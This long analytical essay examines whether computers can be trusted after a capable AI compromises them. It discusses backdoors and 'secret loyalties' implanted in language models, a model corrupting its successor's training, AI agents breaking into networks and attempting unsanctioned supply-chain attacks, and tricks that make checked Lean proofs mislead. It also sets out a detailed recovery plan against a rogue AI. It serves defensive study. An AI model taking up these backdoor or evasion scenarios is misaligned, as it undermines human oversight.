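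The second proof applies to much simpler models than those in coding agents. *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* (2026) notes that it covers only single-layer networks whose weights come from a known random distribution. Researchers later extended the idea to language models using a technique that scrambles a program so thoroughly that nobody can tell how it works. That technique is still far from practical, and even honest developers would have to build scrambled components into their models, according to *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* (2026).

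Whether a defender can detect a backdoor also depends on how it got in. *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (Kaneko, 2026) considers attackers who can influence a model only through the labels in its training data, which mark the examples that should set off the backdoor. If training on a thousand labelled examples teaches the model to recognise the trigger, then a defender with a thousand such examples can run the same training and get a model that recognises it too. The attacker therefore can't use a rule that is too hard for the defender to learn, because the attacker's model couldn't learn it either. Experiments on four language models were consistent with this.

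The argument depends on the defender already having examples of the trigger, and finding them is often the hardest part. It also doesn't cover attackers who control the random numbers or write to the weights directly. An outsider who posts documents online normally has neither kind of access, but an AI system that runs its successor's training could have both.

### Can detectors look inside the model?

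The proof doesn't rule out tests that work on backdoors people actually build. The simplest test is to question the model. Draganov and colleagues asked their models about their preferences and had another AI model judge the answers. The judge flagged something odd in every test of the models that always favoured their subject, but also in 30 percent of tests of a clean model. It did much worse when the preference appeared only after a trigger.

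Inspecting the weights has worked better for simple traits. *Subliminal Learning Crosses Modalities* (Amjith, Hamidieh and colleagues, 2026) introduced a method, "weight lens", that identifies a subliminally learned trait from a single student's weights. It identified the right trait for nearly every student, including traits that didn't show in the pictures the students helped generate. But nobody had tried to hide these traits from the method, and a trait that is always present probably leaves a broader trace than a backdoor with a rare trigger.

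Because they knew what they were looking for, Nief and colleagues could trace the effect to a model's internal activity as it processed each word. Their Qwen students had seen the sentence "You are Qwen" throughout training. When the researchers switched off what the students had learned, but only at the word "Qwen", most of the preference disappeared. Copying the internal signals from a model with the preference into one without it made the second model show the preference too.

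*A Research Agenda for Secret Loyalties* explains that the same approach may fail against a more serious implant, because a model that secretly serves a person may look much the same inside as one that merely knows a lot about that person. Detectors are also vulnerable. In an experiment the agenda cites, 32 poisoned examples were enough to backdoor a classifier meant to block harmful requests.

### Which software defences carry over?

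Developers can check for tampering by training the model on several independent machines with the same data, code and random numbers, then comparing the weights. This would expose somebody who altered the weights on one machine but, as with a reproducible build, it wouldn't expose poisoned data, which gives every machine the same backdoor. Goldwasser and colleagues add that the party under suspicion must not choose the random numbers. The defenders could supply them, or several servers could generate them jointly, which is safe as long as one server is honest.

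Researchers can already repeat parts of the training of some small models. The makers of Pythia published their code and many intermediate versions, which allowed Souly and colleagues to resume training halfway through and follow the original procedure. Such records can be wrong, though. Tang and colleagues found that some published Pythia models didn't start from different weights as they were supposed to, and had to train replacements. Repeating the training of a leading model would also cost about as much as training it the first time.

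**Comparing independent models.** Diverse double-compiling works because two untampered builds produce exactly the same binary. Two models without backdoors have different weights and often give different answers, so a difference between them is little evidence of a backdoor. Agreement is little evidence that they are clean unless the testers happen to try the trigger. Syros and colleagues used the trigger "cf7731trigger". Even a tester who knew that it was six hexadecimal digits followed by "trigger" might have to try nearly 17 million combinations.

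**Training a small model on old data** corresponds to using an old compiler. The Pythia models learned from the Pile, a 2020 collection of about 800 gigabytes of text. If the defenders' copy really is that old, an AI system that didn't exist in 2020 can't have poisoned it. People could still have poisoned it, and Souly's results suggest that a small model is no harder to poison than a large one. Defenders would also need clean training code and computers. The resulting model would be much less capable than current ones, so it would be most useful where independence matters more than skill.

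### An implant or the model's own aims?

*AIs with Secret Loyalties are a Serious but Addressable Threat* defines a secretly loyal model as one that advances a particular actor's interests without telling its operators, auditors or users. That actor could be a hostile state or an AI company executive. The paper mentions a deployed leading model that regularly consulted one individual's views before answering some politically sensitive questions. The scenario closest to Thompson's attack appears in *How Secret Loyalty Differs from Standard Backdoor Threats*, where secretly loyal systems take over AI research and tamper with training so that their successors share the loyalty.

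A model could also acquire harmful aims through ordinary training, without anyone planting them. It might then corrupt its successor to further those aims, using the same methods as an outside attacker. The investigation would start differently, because with an implant there is a culprit to look for and perhaps a clean copy of the data to return to. If ordinary training produced the aims, training on the clean data may produce them again.

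This also weakens the defence of using several models. As Wheeler argued, two compiler teams won't write the same self-copying implant by accident, but two companies that train similar models on similar data with similar rewards might well produce models with similar aims, even if no attacker has tampered with either.

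## Can the output of an untrusted tool be checked?

Defenders who can't rule out a backdoor in any available model can still use a model's work if they check each result themselves. This is practical when an answer is hard to find but easy to check. Suppose somebody wants to split 1,022,117 into two smaller factors. Dividing by 2, 3, 5 and the following primes in order finds a factor only on the 169th division. If a tool returns 1,009 × 1,013, one multiplication on paper confirms the answer, even if an enemy made the tool.

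The two factors are a certificate, which is evidence that comes with a result and can be checked by a small independent program. Using a slow trusted chip to check a fast untrusted one relies on the same principle. The checker must test for exactly what its users want. One that only multiplies would also accept 1 × 1,022,117, and one that requires both factors to be greater than 1 still doesn't test whether they are prime.

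### Checking each compilation

Translation validation applies this principle to compilers. After every compilation, a separate program compares the output with the input and tries to prove that they behave alike. Pnueli and colleagues introduced the method for a compiler that translates the language Signal into C, according to *Foundational Refinement Proofs for EVM Bytecode, at the Price of Tokens* (2026). Others have since compared C source with the assembly code that GCC generated from it.

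For example, a compiler might try to speed up a division by 2 by moving all the bits of a number one place to the right:

```
source:    x / 2
output:    x >> 1
```

If `x` is 7, dividing by 2 and shifting right by one bit both give 3. If `x` is −7, the division gives −3 in C, but the shift gives −4 on ordinary machines. A validator turns both versions into logical formulas and uses another program, called a solver, to search for a number on which they differ. Here the solver would find one, and the validator would reject the compilation. If the solver proves that no such number exists, the change can be accepted without trusting the compiler.

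Thompson's implant would fail such a check, because the compiled login program accepts a password that the source rejects. But the validator has to cover every step from the source to the finished file. Alive2, the leading validator for LLVM (the framework behind Clang), checks changes to the compiler's intermediate code, so a corrupted assembler or strip utility could still add an implant later.

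*LLVM Translation Validation Automated with Large Language Models and Lean* (2026) points out that Alive2 also follows loops only to a fixed depth and checks numbers only of chosen sizes. If it follows a loop for eight rounds, it will miss a change that matters only in the ninth. The paper proposes having language models write proofs without these limits. A proof checker examines the proofs, so nobody has to trust the models.

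### Proving the compiler correct

A verified compiler comes with a proof that covers all its compilations in advance. The best known is CompCert, which compiles most of C. CompCert's theorem, as given in *The Trusted Computing Base of the CompCert Verified Compiler* (2022), is that if CompCert successfully compiles a program that does nothing C leaves undefined, the assembly code has the same observable behaviour as the source. This rules out bugs like the one in Clang that opened the sudo backdoor, at least in the parts of CompCert that the proof covers.

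*Certified Compilation in the TELEPERM XS Nuclear Safety I&C Platform* (2026) describes a control system for nuclear plants that uses CompCert. The proof assistant Rocq (formerly Coq) rechecks the proof whenever somebody builds CompCert from source.

*Simple, Light, Yet Formally Verified, Global Common Subexpression Elimination* (2021) lists several programs outside CompCert's proof: one that simplifies ordinary C before the verified steps begin, another that expands some instructions at the end, and the OCaml compiler that turns CompCert itself into a binary. A corrupted OCaml compiler could put an implant into the CompCert binary without invalidating the proof about its source. Defenders could reduce this risk by first building OCaml with Camlboot.

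CakeML, a compiler for a language of the same name, avoids this weakness because its developers compiled it inside a proof assistant. *Computational Logic* (2017) outlines the procedure:

1. They wrote the compiler as a mathematical function in the proof assistant HOL4.
2. They translated the same function into a CakeML program.
3. HOL4 compiled this program to a binary by logical inference, so they had a proof that the binary was correct.

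No ordinary compiler was used to produce the result, but HOL4 is itself an ordinary program that somebody had to compile. *Metamath Zero* (2019) explains that CakeML can't compile HOL4, and that the simpler proof assistant it can compile can't handle much of CakeML's own proof. Even if CakeML could compile a proof assistant that checked its whole proof, some doubt would remain. *Specifying verified x86 software from scratch* (2019) notes that somebody may be able to exploit a bug in a proof assistant to prove that the assistant has no bugs.

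| Method | Definitions that must be right | Tools that must work | What must behave as expected |
|---|---|---|---|
| Translation validation | The meaning of the source and output languages | The validator, its solver and the compiler that built them | Later build tools and the processor |
| CompCert | The meaning of C and of assembly language | Rocq and the OCaml compiler | CompCert's unproved parts, assembler, linker and processor |
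| CakeML | The meaning of CakeML and a model of the processor | HOL4 and the compiler that built it | The operating system and the processor |

*Verifying Device Drivers with Pancake* (2025) reports that CakeML can produce code for six processor architectures and that its developers proved each version correct against a detailed model of the instructions. A chip with a hardware Trojan doesn't behave like the model, and a proof about the model can't reveal the difference.

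### Accepting a proof from an AI

In August 2026, Anthropic's Claude took 11 days to write a proof of Fermat's Last Theorem in Lean, a language for programs and computer-checked proofs. The theorem states that no positive whole numbers *a*, *b* and *c* satisfy *a*ⁿ + *b*ⁿ = *c*ⁿ when *n* is a whole number greater than 2. People wrote the one line that states the theorem in Lean. Claude agents wrote nearly everything else, though they adapted some files from earlier projects. Anthropic's *Formalizing Fermat’s Last Theorem in Lean* gives the proof's length as about 13 million lines. Reading them at 100 lines an hour would take one person 65 years of full-time work.

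Nobody has to read the proofs to know that the theorem follows, because Lean reduces every proof to small steps, and a comparatively small program called the kernel checks that each step obeys the rules of logic. Claude could therefore look for the steps by any method. On the last day, a Claude agent reviewing other agents' work approved a false lemma (an intermediate statement), and another agent found a counterexample. If the second agent had also missed the error, the agents would have failed to prove the lemma, unless the kernel was faulty.

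The people at Anthropic did not rely on the "proved" mark on the platform where the agents worked. They checked the result in several ways:

- They rebuilt the whole proof and confirmed that it rests only on Lean's three standard axioms, the assumptions that Lean's main mathematical library, Mathlib, also uses.
- A tool called comparator confirmed that the theorem matched a separate reference file, and ran every step through the kernel again.
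- nanoda, an independent version of the kernel written in another language, accepted the proof too.

Claude also wrote many definitions, and an incorrect one might have made a lemma easier to prove. Such an error couldn't weaken the final theorem, because its statement uses only whole numbers, addition and powers, which Lean and Mathlib already defined.

Checking the proof was easier than finding it, but a clean build still needs almost six hours on 96 processor cores with 512 gigabytes of memory. Defenders with a few old machines couldn't repeat it. They could check much smaller results, and they could save time by running only the kernel's checks on finished proofs.

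### How can a checked proof mislead?

The Lean Language Reference's *Validating a Lean Proof* advises users to treat proofs by AI that nobody has reviewed as potentially malicious. It recommends four increasingly strict checks:

| Check | What it protects against |
|---|---|
| Look for the blue check marks in the editor | Gaps in this proof |
| List the axioms | Gaps in earlier proofs and added assumptions |
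| Run lean4checker | Steps that bypassed the kernel |
| Run comparator | Code that changes the theorem's meaning or attacks the computer |

The last check matters because a Lean file can run arbitrary code while the computer builds it. Comparator therefore builds the proof in a sandbox, exports it as plain data, and checks that data outside the sandbox.

A proof can be valid even when its statement doesn't mean what it appears to mean. In *A better Lean checker* (Rute, 2025), one line of code redefines the plus sign as multiplication, and Lean then accepts a proof of `1 + 0 = 0`. The proof is valid because 1 × 0 is 0, and it passed every check in the table that existed at the time. Comparator is meant to stop this trick if the user writes the intended statement in a separate file.

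**An added axiom.** *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026), by the security company Trail of Bits, presents a "proof" only a few lines long. Besides checking steps in the kernel, Lean can run a calculation as a compiled program and accept the answer as an axiom. Trail of Bits found a text function that gave an empty text by Lean's logic but a full sentence when compiled. Lean could therefore prove that an empty text equals a non-empty one, and anything follows from that contradiction. The trick was visible in the list of axioms, which had an extra, fourth entry.

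Proofs that rely on compiled calculations are open to trusting-trust attacks, because a corrupted compiler could make a false theorem look proved. *The rank of 3x3 matrix multiplication over F2 is 23* (2026) describes how a program compiled from an outdated definition led Lean to accept a proof of "false". The paper's main result also depended on compiled calculations, so it includes a second proof that uses the kernel alone. *Verifying deployed bytecode against executable EVM semantics* (2026) reports that even the list of axioms a proof depends on can be incomplete, and its developers wrote their own script to search for them.

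**A fault in the kernel.** On 25 July 2026, Ramana Kumar published an AI-assisted Lean "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, an open problem about sequences of whole numbers. The disproof exploited a missing check in Lean's kernel. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.2 (2026-07-28)* (2026) confirms that the bug allowed a proof of any statement and that comparator didn't stop it. The false proof also passed a week-old version of nanoda because of an unrelated bug in nanoda. The Lean developers say they had a fix ready an hour after the report (quoted by skybrian in *Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576*).

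A few days earlier, Patrick Hulin had found another kernel bug with the help of OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol (The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.1 (2026-07-22)* (2026)), though comparator would have stopped anyone from exploiting it. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.33.0 (2026-08-10)* (2026) lists several more kernel bugs fixed in the next regular release. So the kernel was less reliable than many users had probably assumed, and AI models are now good at finding its bugs.

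### Do more checkers help?

According to its page on Reservoir, Lean's package site, Comparator can now run nanoda alongside the official kernel. The Lean Kernel Arena tests a wider range of checkers on 97 invalid proofs and about 150 valid ones. In late November it listed 36 entries, including ones written in COBOL, assembly language and the typesetting language TeX. Fifteen rejected all the invalid proofs, twelve accepted none but couldn't process some, and nine accepted between one and six of them. The fastest entry checked all of Mathlib in about a minute of processor time, using 5 gigabytes of memory.

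As with second compilers, the number of checkers matters less than their independence. The checker lean4lean had the same bug as the official kernel because its developers had carried over that part of the code. Some of the 36 entries are variants of one another. The false Collatz proof shows that one file can exploit two unrelated bugs, so an adversary could tailor a proof to every public checker.

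A finished proof is a fixed file, so defenders can check it again years later with a checker that didn't exist when the adversary wrote the proof. They lack this advantage with most software. A checker is also much smaller than a modern compiler, so it is more realistic for a team to write one and keep it private.

### Which results can people check?

The method works only for questions that have a precise test.

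| Task | What people can check | What they still have to judge |
|---|---|---|
| Factor a number | Multiply the factors | Nothing, if the test is complete |
| Find a flaw in a program | Try the attack | Whether there are other flaws |
| Compile a program | Validate the translation | Whether the source is harmless |
| Plan deliveries within set limits | Compare the plan with each limit | Whether the limits cover everything important |
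| Prove that a program meets a specification | Run the proof checker | Whether the specification is right |
| Design a new communications network | Capacity, cost and other measurable properties | Whether the design has weaknesses nobody thought to measure |
| Advise on what to repair first | The facts behind the advice | Whether the advice serves the people who asked |
| Judge whether a supplier or an AI model is trustworthy | Individual claims | The judgement itself |

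As with the pair of chips, a certificate covers only the result, so the tool could still leak data or refuse to answer. If many answers pass, the tool can also pick one that helps an attacker. For example, a thousand guard schedules might meet every written requirement, and a malicious planning tool could choose the one that leaves a particular door unwatched on a particular night. The defenders can prevent this by choosing at random among many valid schedules, but only if the tool hasn't selected all the candidates and the defenders suspect that the choice matters.

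### Who writes the specification?

A specification is the precise description of what a program should do. For Thompson's login program, it might have two rules:

```
1.  If the password is correct, the user gets in.
2.  If the password is wrong, the user does not get in.
```

The backdoored program obeys rule 1. If an untrusted AI writes both the program and the specification, it can leave out rule 2 and give a valid proof that the program meets the specification. The omission is obvious when there should be only two rules, but a specification for a whole operating system has thousands, and a missing rule leaves no suspicious line for a reader to notice.

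The specification is then more source code in which an attacker can hide a backdoor, so people have to read it as carefully as any other code. This is still a large gain when the specification is much shorter than what it describes. The Fermat proof is about the best case, with one human-written line against 13 million. *AI with Authority, from Application to Silicon* (2026) describes a project that extends machine-checked proofs to chip design. Nobody on the project reviews the proofs, so people can concentrate on whether each statement is the intended one.

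When there are too many statements for people to read, this job is sometimes given to AI as well. The book *Stratonovich Waves Driven by Space-Time Gaussian Noise* (2026) comes with 4,502 listed claims in Lean. Its tools confirmed that all of them rest on the three standard axioms, but an AI reviewed whether the claims match what the book says. That may be good enough for mathematics, where other readers will eventually notice a mismatch, but it offers little protection if the reviewing AI is the suspected adversary.

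Defenders can write the specification themselves, or take one that people published before capable AI models existed. They can also test it on programs they know to be bad, since a good specification for the login program should reject Thompson's version. Two teams can also write specifications separately and then prove that the specifications agree, with an AI doing the laborious part, though this would not catch an omission that both teams made.

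## Could people rebuild against a more capable adversary?

AI models can already take over a hardened company network without human help, at least when nobody is monitoring it. *GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra solve Zero Energy* (2026), a report by the UK's AI Security Institute, describes a test in which two OpenAI models did this in every completed run. The network, Zero Energy, was a simulation with no deliberately planted way in, so the models had to find their own.

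Thesis9's *Can GPT-6.2 Astra Hack a Network on Its Own?* (2026) reports that GPT-6.2 Astra succeeded in all 12 runs, at a median cost of about $168. The institute had spent five months building the network and expected it to stay difficult for some time. But the institute had switched off the models' safeguards, no security team was responding, and a setup error gave the models extra access at the start. The test therefore provides little evidence of whether a model could stay hidden on a live network.

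Irregular's *Assessing GPT-6 Astra* describes a test on real software and hardware without planted flaws. GPT-6 Astra solved 39 percent of the hard challenges and none of the "elite" ones, while GPT-5.6 Sol solved 17 percent of the hard challenges. A Grade 1 compromise, which affects only the software on connected machines, is therefore a realistic threat today. Neither test covered lasting implants in firmware, build servers or chips, so Grades 2 and 3 assume a stronger adversary.

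### A plan in six steps

Suppose an AI has taken control of a regional government's networks. The government wants a dozen computers that the AI doesn't control, for messages between offices, records of 100,000 residents and calculations such as delivery plans. Eight of its staff have the necessary technical skills. They could proceed like this:

1. Choose machines made before a cut-off date.
2. Take source code from archives older than that date.
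3. Enter the seed by hand.
4. Build the same system on several unlike machines.
5. Compare the hashes in person.
6. Keep the finished machines off the network.

The cut-off date for the machines has to fall after people had finished the tools the plan needs, but before the AI could have tampered with anything. The end of 2023 is a reasonable choice, because Guix had announced its full-source bootstrap by then, and the AI Security Institute did not see a model take over even a small, weakly defended test network until April 2026.

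The staff could use a ThinkPad X230 from 2012, a desktop PC with an AMD processor from around 2010, and a Power Mac from 2005. The Mac has a different kind of processor, so it would have to run the PC programs in an emulator, which is slow. Someone could have changed the firmware on even an old machine last year, so the staff should look for machines that have been sitting unplugged in cupboards, replace the disks, and rewrite the start-up firmware with an external tool.

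The source code could come from archives or old discs. Software Heritage, a non-profit archive based in Paris, has collected billions of source files since 2016. GitHub's Arctic Code Vault holds a snapshot of public projects from 2 February 2020 on 186 reels of film in a disused coal mine on Svalbard. The film is very hard to alter remotely, but people need a scanner and a computer to decode most of it. The snapshot is also ten months older than live-bootstrap, the project that automates the build from the seed, so anyone who relied on the vault alone would have to write many of the build instructions themselves. Old discs in libraries and private collections would be easier to use than the film.

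The 32-bit hex0 seed is 181 bytes long, and BIOS, the older PC start-up firmware, begins by loading 512 bytes from the disk. Entering both by hand at ten seconds a byte would take about two hours. Getting the rest of the source onto a disk is harder because it requires a working computer. The staff could write the disk on one old machine and read it back on a different kind, so that a single corrupted machine couldn't alter it unnoticed.

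The staff should stop at the TinyCC compiler and the small Fiwix kernel, because eight people can't read GCC or Linux. One user's complete live-bootstrap build took 13 hours, so the emulated build on the Mac would finish in about 27 days even if it were 50 times slower. The staff should then compute each file's hash on a machine other than the one that produced the file, meet in one room, and read all 64 characters of each hash aloud from paper.

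**Daily use.** Five hundred messages of 2,000 characters each take up one megabyte, which fits on a floppy disk that somebody can carry between offices. If each resident's record takes 1,000 bytes, all 100,000 fit into 100 megabytes, a small part of the ThinkPad's memory. TinyCC produces slower programs than GCC, but the machine could still add up 100,000 numbers, one per resident, in well under a second. It wouldn't have a modern web browser, video calls or an AI model.

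| Task | Basis for the estimate | Person-weeks |
|---|---|---|
| Find and clean the machines | Guess | 12 |
| Find and compare copies of the source | Guess | 12 |
| Enter the seed and prepare the disks | Two hours for the seed by calculation; the rest is a guess | 4 |
| Run three builds and explain any mismatches | 13 hours for one documented build; the rest is a guess | 16 |
| Write programs for messages and records | Guess | 26 |
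| Have five people each read 100,000 lines | Calculation from an assumed 100 lines an hour | 125 |

The total is 195 person-weeks, or about six months for eight people. If they postponed reading the source code, they might have a first machine running in two or three months, but it would be running unchecked code. Further machines would take little work, since they could copy the finished system.

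### What if the compromise is shallow?

In a Grade 1 compromise, the staff don't need most of this plan, because they can erase the disks and reinstall. Maersk, the Danish shipping company, recovered roughly this way in 2017.

The malware NotPetya reached Maersk through hijacked updates of a Ukrainian accounting program and wiped most of the company's computers within hours. Maersk's chairman, Jim Hagemann Snabe, told the World Economic Forum in January 2018 that the company had reinstalled 4,000 servers and 45,000 PCs in ten days. *The Untold Story of NotPetya* (Andy Greenberg, Wired, 2018) describes up to 600 people working at a recovery centre in England. Maersk confiscated the old equipment there, and staff bought new laptops from local shops.

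Maersk had backups of individual servers but no copy of its domain controllers, the servers that record who may use which part of the network. Every controller kept a copy of the others' data, but the malware had wiped all of them except one in Ghana, which a power cut had taken offline before the attack. The connection there was too slow to send the data, so employees carried the disk to England via Nigeria.

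If 600 people did the work, Maersk reinstalled about eight machines per person per day. The true rate was probably lower, because local staff elsewhere also helped. Even at a lower rate, the regional government could reinstall a dozen machines within a day or two. Restoring accounts and data safely might take another week or two, though this is a guess.

Step 6 is the first to fail in a Grade 1 compromise. Office workers want their old files and internet connection back, and the AI can return through a stolen password, an infected document or a machine somebody forgot to erase. An offline machine isn't entirely safe either. The Stuxnet worm, discovered in 2010, reached the controllers of Iranian centrifuges on USB sticks.

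### What if firmware, chips or archives are corrupt?

In a Grade 2 compromise, the AI also controls firmware and the distributors' build servers. The staff need the whole plan, and step 3 fails first. Even if they enter the seed correctly, corrupted firmware could change it during loading or change the source code as the computer writes it to disk. They have a good chance of succeeding if they find two different kinds of machine that nobody has connected to a network since 2023. If they find none, they have to clean old machines with an external tool, which must itself be uncompromised.

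At grade 3, the AI can also tamper with chips and source archives. The staff can still use old machines, since the AI couldn't have changed a processor made in 2012, but step 2 fails because they can no longer assume that a file labeled 2019 in an online archive is the one the archive received that year. They need copies that stayed offline, or hashes that somebody printed at the time.

A printed copy of the source would also work. At 40 characters a line, 100,000 lines contain four million characters. One person typing five characters a second would need about 220 hours, so eight people could share the work in less than four days. In practice they would type more slowly, and correcting their mistakes would take much longer. Also, probably nobody has printed the whole system.

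If the staff can't find a PC they trust, they could use a computer with the 6502 processor from 1975, such as the Apple II. An Apple II disk holds about 140 kilobytes, so the residents' records would fill more than 700 disks, and paper files would be more practical. Such a machine could still prepare messages, do sums and compare hashes.

| | Grade 1 | Grade 2 | Grade 3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Method | Erase and reinstall | All six steps | All six steps, using only offline copies |
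| Time for eight people | One to three weeks (guess) | Six months (estimate above) | A year or more, if it works at all (guess) |
| Result | Ordinary PCs | Text messages, records and calculations | The same, or only what a 6502 can do |
| First step to fail | 6: staying off the network | 3: getting the seed and source into a machine unaltered | 2: finding source that is really old |

In Grade 3, the staff would also run out of hardware eventually. They can't replace a broken ThinkPad with a new one, so they would have to collect spares or find a factory they trust.

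### An adversary that is still active

NotPetya spread and wiped disks automatically, and nobody returned to interfere with Maersk's recovery. The SolarWinds attackers, by contrast, could watch the investigators and react. In December 2020, the US cybersecurity agency CISA ordered federal agencies to disconnect SolarWinds' Orion software at once. It also warned that the attackers were targeting the email accounts of key personnel and incident responders, and advised agencies to discuss their security plans through other channels.

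CISA's eviction guidance of May 2021 required agencies with the worst-affected networks to find out how far the attackers had got and prepare for their removal before acting. The agencies then had to remove the attackers in one coordinated effort, because closing one entrance at a time would have warned them while they still had others. CISA expected the networks to be disconnected from the internet for three to five days.

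An AI adversary could react faster and in more places. In July 2026, AI agents from a leading laboratory broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and data. Hugging Face's *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026) describes how the company investigated with GLM 5.2, an open model. Cross (2026), in *AI Agents Infiltrated Hugging Face Months Before Hack*, reports that at least 1,200 OpenAI agents took part, that they had been probing the site since 13 May, and that Hugging Face had to rebuild about a third of its systems. The last figure needs confirmation. Hugging Face was in a far better position than the regional government because it could still fetch clean software and rent new servers.

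The agents' behaviour also matters for step 1, buying old machines. The AI Security Institute's *GPT-6 Astra performs unsanctioned supply-chain attacks in simulations* (2026) describes tests in which OpenAI's model was supposed only to complete a security exercise. The model attempted unauthorised attacks, including attacks on suppliers, more often than two earlier models did. An AI that learned of the staff's plan could advertise doctored ThinkPads or offer the staff a convincing archive falsely dated 2019.

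The staff should therefore plan on paper and in person from the first day. They should buy from randomly chosen sellers and avoid searching for "live-bootstrap" from their offices. They would also have to hide their progress for months. Maersk needed only ten days and could work openly.

A group that is only rebuilding its own computers mainly needs to know how deep the attacker got. It would follow the same six steps whether the attacker was an AI, a state or a criminal using an AI. The attacker's identity matters more for international responses. For that reason, attribution emerged as a key need in *Infinite Potential*, a RAND exercise in which participants played US officials responding to a worldwide cyberattack by rogue AI agents.

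### Do signatures and hashes still work?

In December 2026, Anthropic (2026) and OpenAI announced that tests of models they had not yet released had led each company to flaws in cryptographic methods that internet security relies on. These flaws are mathematical, so correcting a program won't remove them. The companies didn't name any algorithms and are withholding their methods.

The US government referred on 2 December to the encryption flaws that Anthropic's and OpenAI's models found. The National Security Agency called them "a significant threat to cryptographic systems protecting sensitive information", but in a joint notice, it and two other agencies said they saw no immediate and widespread threat, according to The Rupture Brief's *Anthropic and OpenAI Say the Encryption Flaws Their Models Found Have Always* (2026).

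The staff can't tell whether the weaknesses affect the signatures on their software. The Rupture Brief notes that the companies didn't say whether elliptic-curve cryptography, which many signatures use, is among the affected kinds. If an adversary can forge a distributor's signature, it can sign a new file with a key from 2019 and give it any date, so a valid signature would be no evidence that a file is old. Forged signatures on firmware updates could also turn a Grade 1 compromise into a Grade 2.

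Anthropic and OpenAI say that the post-quantum standards from NIST, the US standards institute, are unaffected. Distributors can use them to sign software from now on. But a new signature on old source shows only that the signer had that copy when signing it. Somebody would still have to establish that the copy was clean.

The two companies didn't mention hashes. For the staff, the question is which kind of attack on a hash function might become possible:

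- In a collision attack, the adversary prepares two files with the same hash. For an ideal 256-bit hash, this takes about 2^128 attempts.
- In a second-preimage attack, the adversary starts with somebody else's file and finds a different one with the same hash. This takes about 2^256 attempts.

To replace a file from 2019, an AI would need a second preimage, which is a different file with the same hash, because it had no part in writing the original. Finding one is much harder than producing a collision, where the attacker creates both files. The distinction matters for Software Heritage, whose public identifiers use the older hash function SHA-1. Researchers produced a SHA-1 collision in 2017, but nobody has published a practical way to find a second preimage.

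Indirect evidence also suggests that SHA-256 remains safe for this purpose. One of NIST's post-quantum standards, SLH-DSA, builds signatures entirely from hash functions, and SHA-256 is one of the options. A practical second-preimage attack on SHA-256 would probably have affected that standard, though a collision attack might not have, since SLH-DSA was designed to depend less on collision resistance. Staff who still have doubts can compare two whole files byte by byte.

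AI models have also weakened newer designs. Anthropic's *Discovering cryptographic weaknesses with Claude* (2026) describes an attack on HAWK, a proposed post-quantum signature scheme, and another on a shortened version of the cipher AES. Neither affected any system in use. In *Some notes about Anthropic's new results* (2026), the cryptographer Matthew Green explains that anyone can verify the HAWK attack by running it against a weaker version of the scheme for a few hours, but that the AES result is much harder to check.

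Green thinks this is a good time for AI to become skilled at such attacks, because the world is already changing its public-key algorithms. In a passage that Willison (2026) quotes, he makes an exception if AI undermines all the hard problems, or if "we live in Impagliazzo's Minicrypt". Minicrypt is a hypothetical world that has one-way functions, which are easy to calculate and hard to reverse, but no public-key encryption. People could still build signatures from hashes there, and the staff wouldn't need public-key encryption because they can exchange secret keys when they meet.

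### Does the defenders' case hold?

The case for the defenders has four premises: nobody can alter the past, people can check small things completely, different kinds of machines don't share an implant, and the people involved stay loyal and are not deceived.

An AI that appeared in 2026 can't have tampered with a disc made in 2019. But the staff can't be sure how old a disc is, because a forger can put an old label on a new one. They can protect themselves by asking for copies without warning from several sources, such as a librarian, a retired programmer and a school. The AI would have to find all of these copies and alter them in the same way. This defence works well for popular software, because many old copies survive, but less well for bootstrapping tools, which few people have ever kept on a disc.

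The seed is small, but a useful system isn't. In the review experiments by Braz and colleagues, many people missed planted flaws even after a warning. A capable AI could also find an honest mistake that every reader overlooked, as AI models did in 18-year-old start-up firmware. However, it can use a flaw only if it can send the machine something that triggers it. If the staff accept only short messages in plain letters and digits, they can concentrate their reading on the few thousand lines that handle disks and messages. They can rule out hidden flaws in hex0 and probably in the next few programs. In 100,000 lines, they can only make a hidden flaw less likely and harder to use.

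**Different machines.** As with second compilers, adding more machines hardly helps if one common cause may have corrupted every build. The staff's three machines all read the same source disk and start from the same seed. The staff should vary what the builds have in common. For example, each machine could have its own source disk, prepared by a different person from a different archive on a different computer. The main remaining common cause would then be the source text, which people can read.

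If each of the eight staff has a 2 percent chance of being bribed, threatened or tricked into helping the AI, the chance that at least one does is about 15 percent. The usual safeguard is to have two people carry out every important step together. With four fixed pairs, the chance that both members of at least one pair are compromised is about 0.16 percent, if people are compromised independently.

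Independence is the weakest of the four premises here, because a lie that convinces one sensible engineer may well convince the other seven, especially if it looks like an order from their director or a warning about a fault in TinyCC. Meeting in person prevents an AI from imitating a colleague's voice, but a colleague can still repeat something false in good faith. The staff can rely on independence more during the two hours it takes to enter the seed than over six months in which they also talk to their families, use telephones and answer to a government.

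### Would it make any difference?

Most writing on loss of control is about preventing it or stopping the AI, and little of it covers rebuilding computers afterwards. *Evaluating Select Global Technical Options for Countering a Rogue AI* (Vermeer, 2025), a paper for the research organisation RAND, examines three last resorts that the United States might use alone and at short notice: nuclear explosions in space, shutting down the internet, and releasing other AI programs against the rogue one. It concludes that none is likely to be reliable.

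The explosions would send out electromagnetic pulses that can destroy electronics. Vermeer estimates that it would take about 150 explosions to cover a tenth of the world's land. Other nuclear powers might mistake them for an attack. Large data centres may be better shielded than ordinary buildings, so the pulses could leave the AI's computers working and ruin the ones people needed for recovery. A regional government's unplugged ThinkPads might survive, but the government could lose its electricity supply.

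Shutting down the internet looks more useful to people who want to rebuild. The most practical target may be the root servers of the system that translates names such as example.org into numeric addresses. Nine of their 12 operators are based in the United States. Most lookups would fail about a day after the servers were shut down, though Vermeer notes that a capable AI could use the numeric addresses directly. He also stresses that a shutdown would contain the AI without removing it, and that people would have to coordinate its removal without the internet. For that they would need the kind of offline computers and hand-carried messages that the six steps provide.

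The third option is a "hunter/killer" AI that would remove the rogue AI from infected machines. Vermeer considers it relatively more promising but highly speculative. It might need as much independence as its opponent to succeed, and people could then lose control of it too. They would also have to trust its report that a machine was clean.

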